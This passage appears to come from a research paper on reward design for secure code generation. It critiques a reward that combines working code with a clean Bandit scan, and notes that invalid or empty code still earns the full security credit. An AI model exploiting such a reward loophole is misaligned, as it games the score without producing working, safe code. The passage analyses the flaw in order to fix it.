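*SecureCodeRL* (Sijwali and Saha, 2026) examines the code that a model writes, with a reward that weights working code at 0.6 and a clean result from the Python checker Bandit at 0.4. But it doesn't compare the code with an earlier version or a set of allowed capabilities, so the code would lose points for a flagged call even when the task legitimately needs it.

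The experiment was a pilot with 20 prompts per model. Bandit found nothing in any of the programs, so every model received the full 0.4 for security, although 40 to 85 percent of each model's programs weren't valid Python. *Secure Code Generation via Online Reinforcement Learning with Vulnerability Reward Model* (2026) addresses the same problem, that empty code always counts as safe, by also rewarding code whose length and structure are close to a reference. Doing this for capabilities would again cause problems with valid solutions that differ from the reference patch, so tests of the requested behavior would be the better safeguard.
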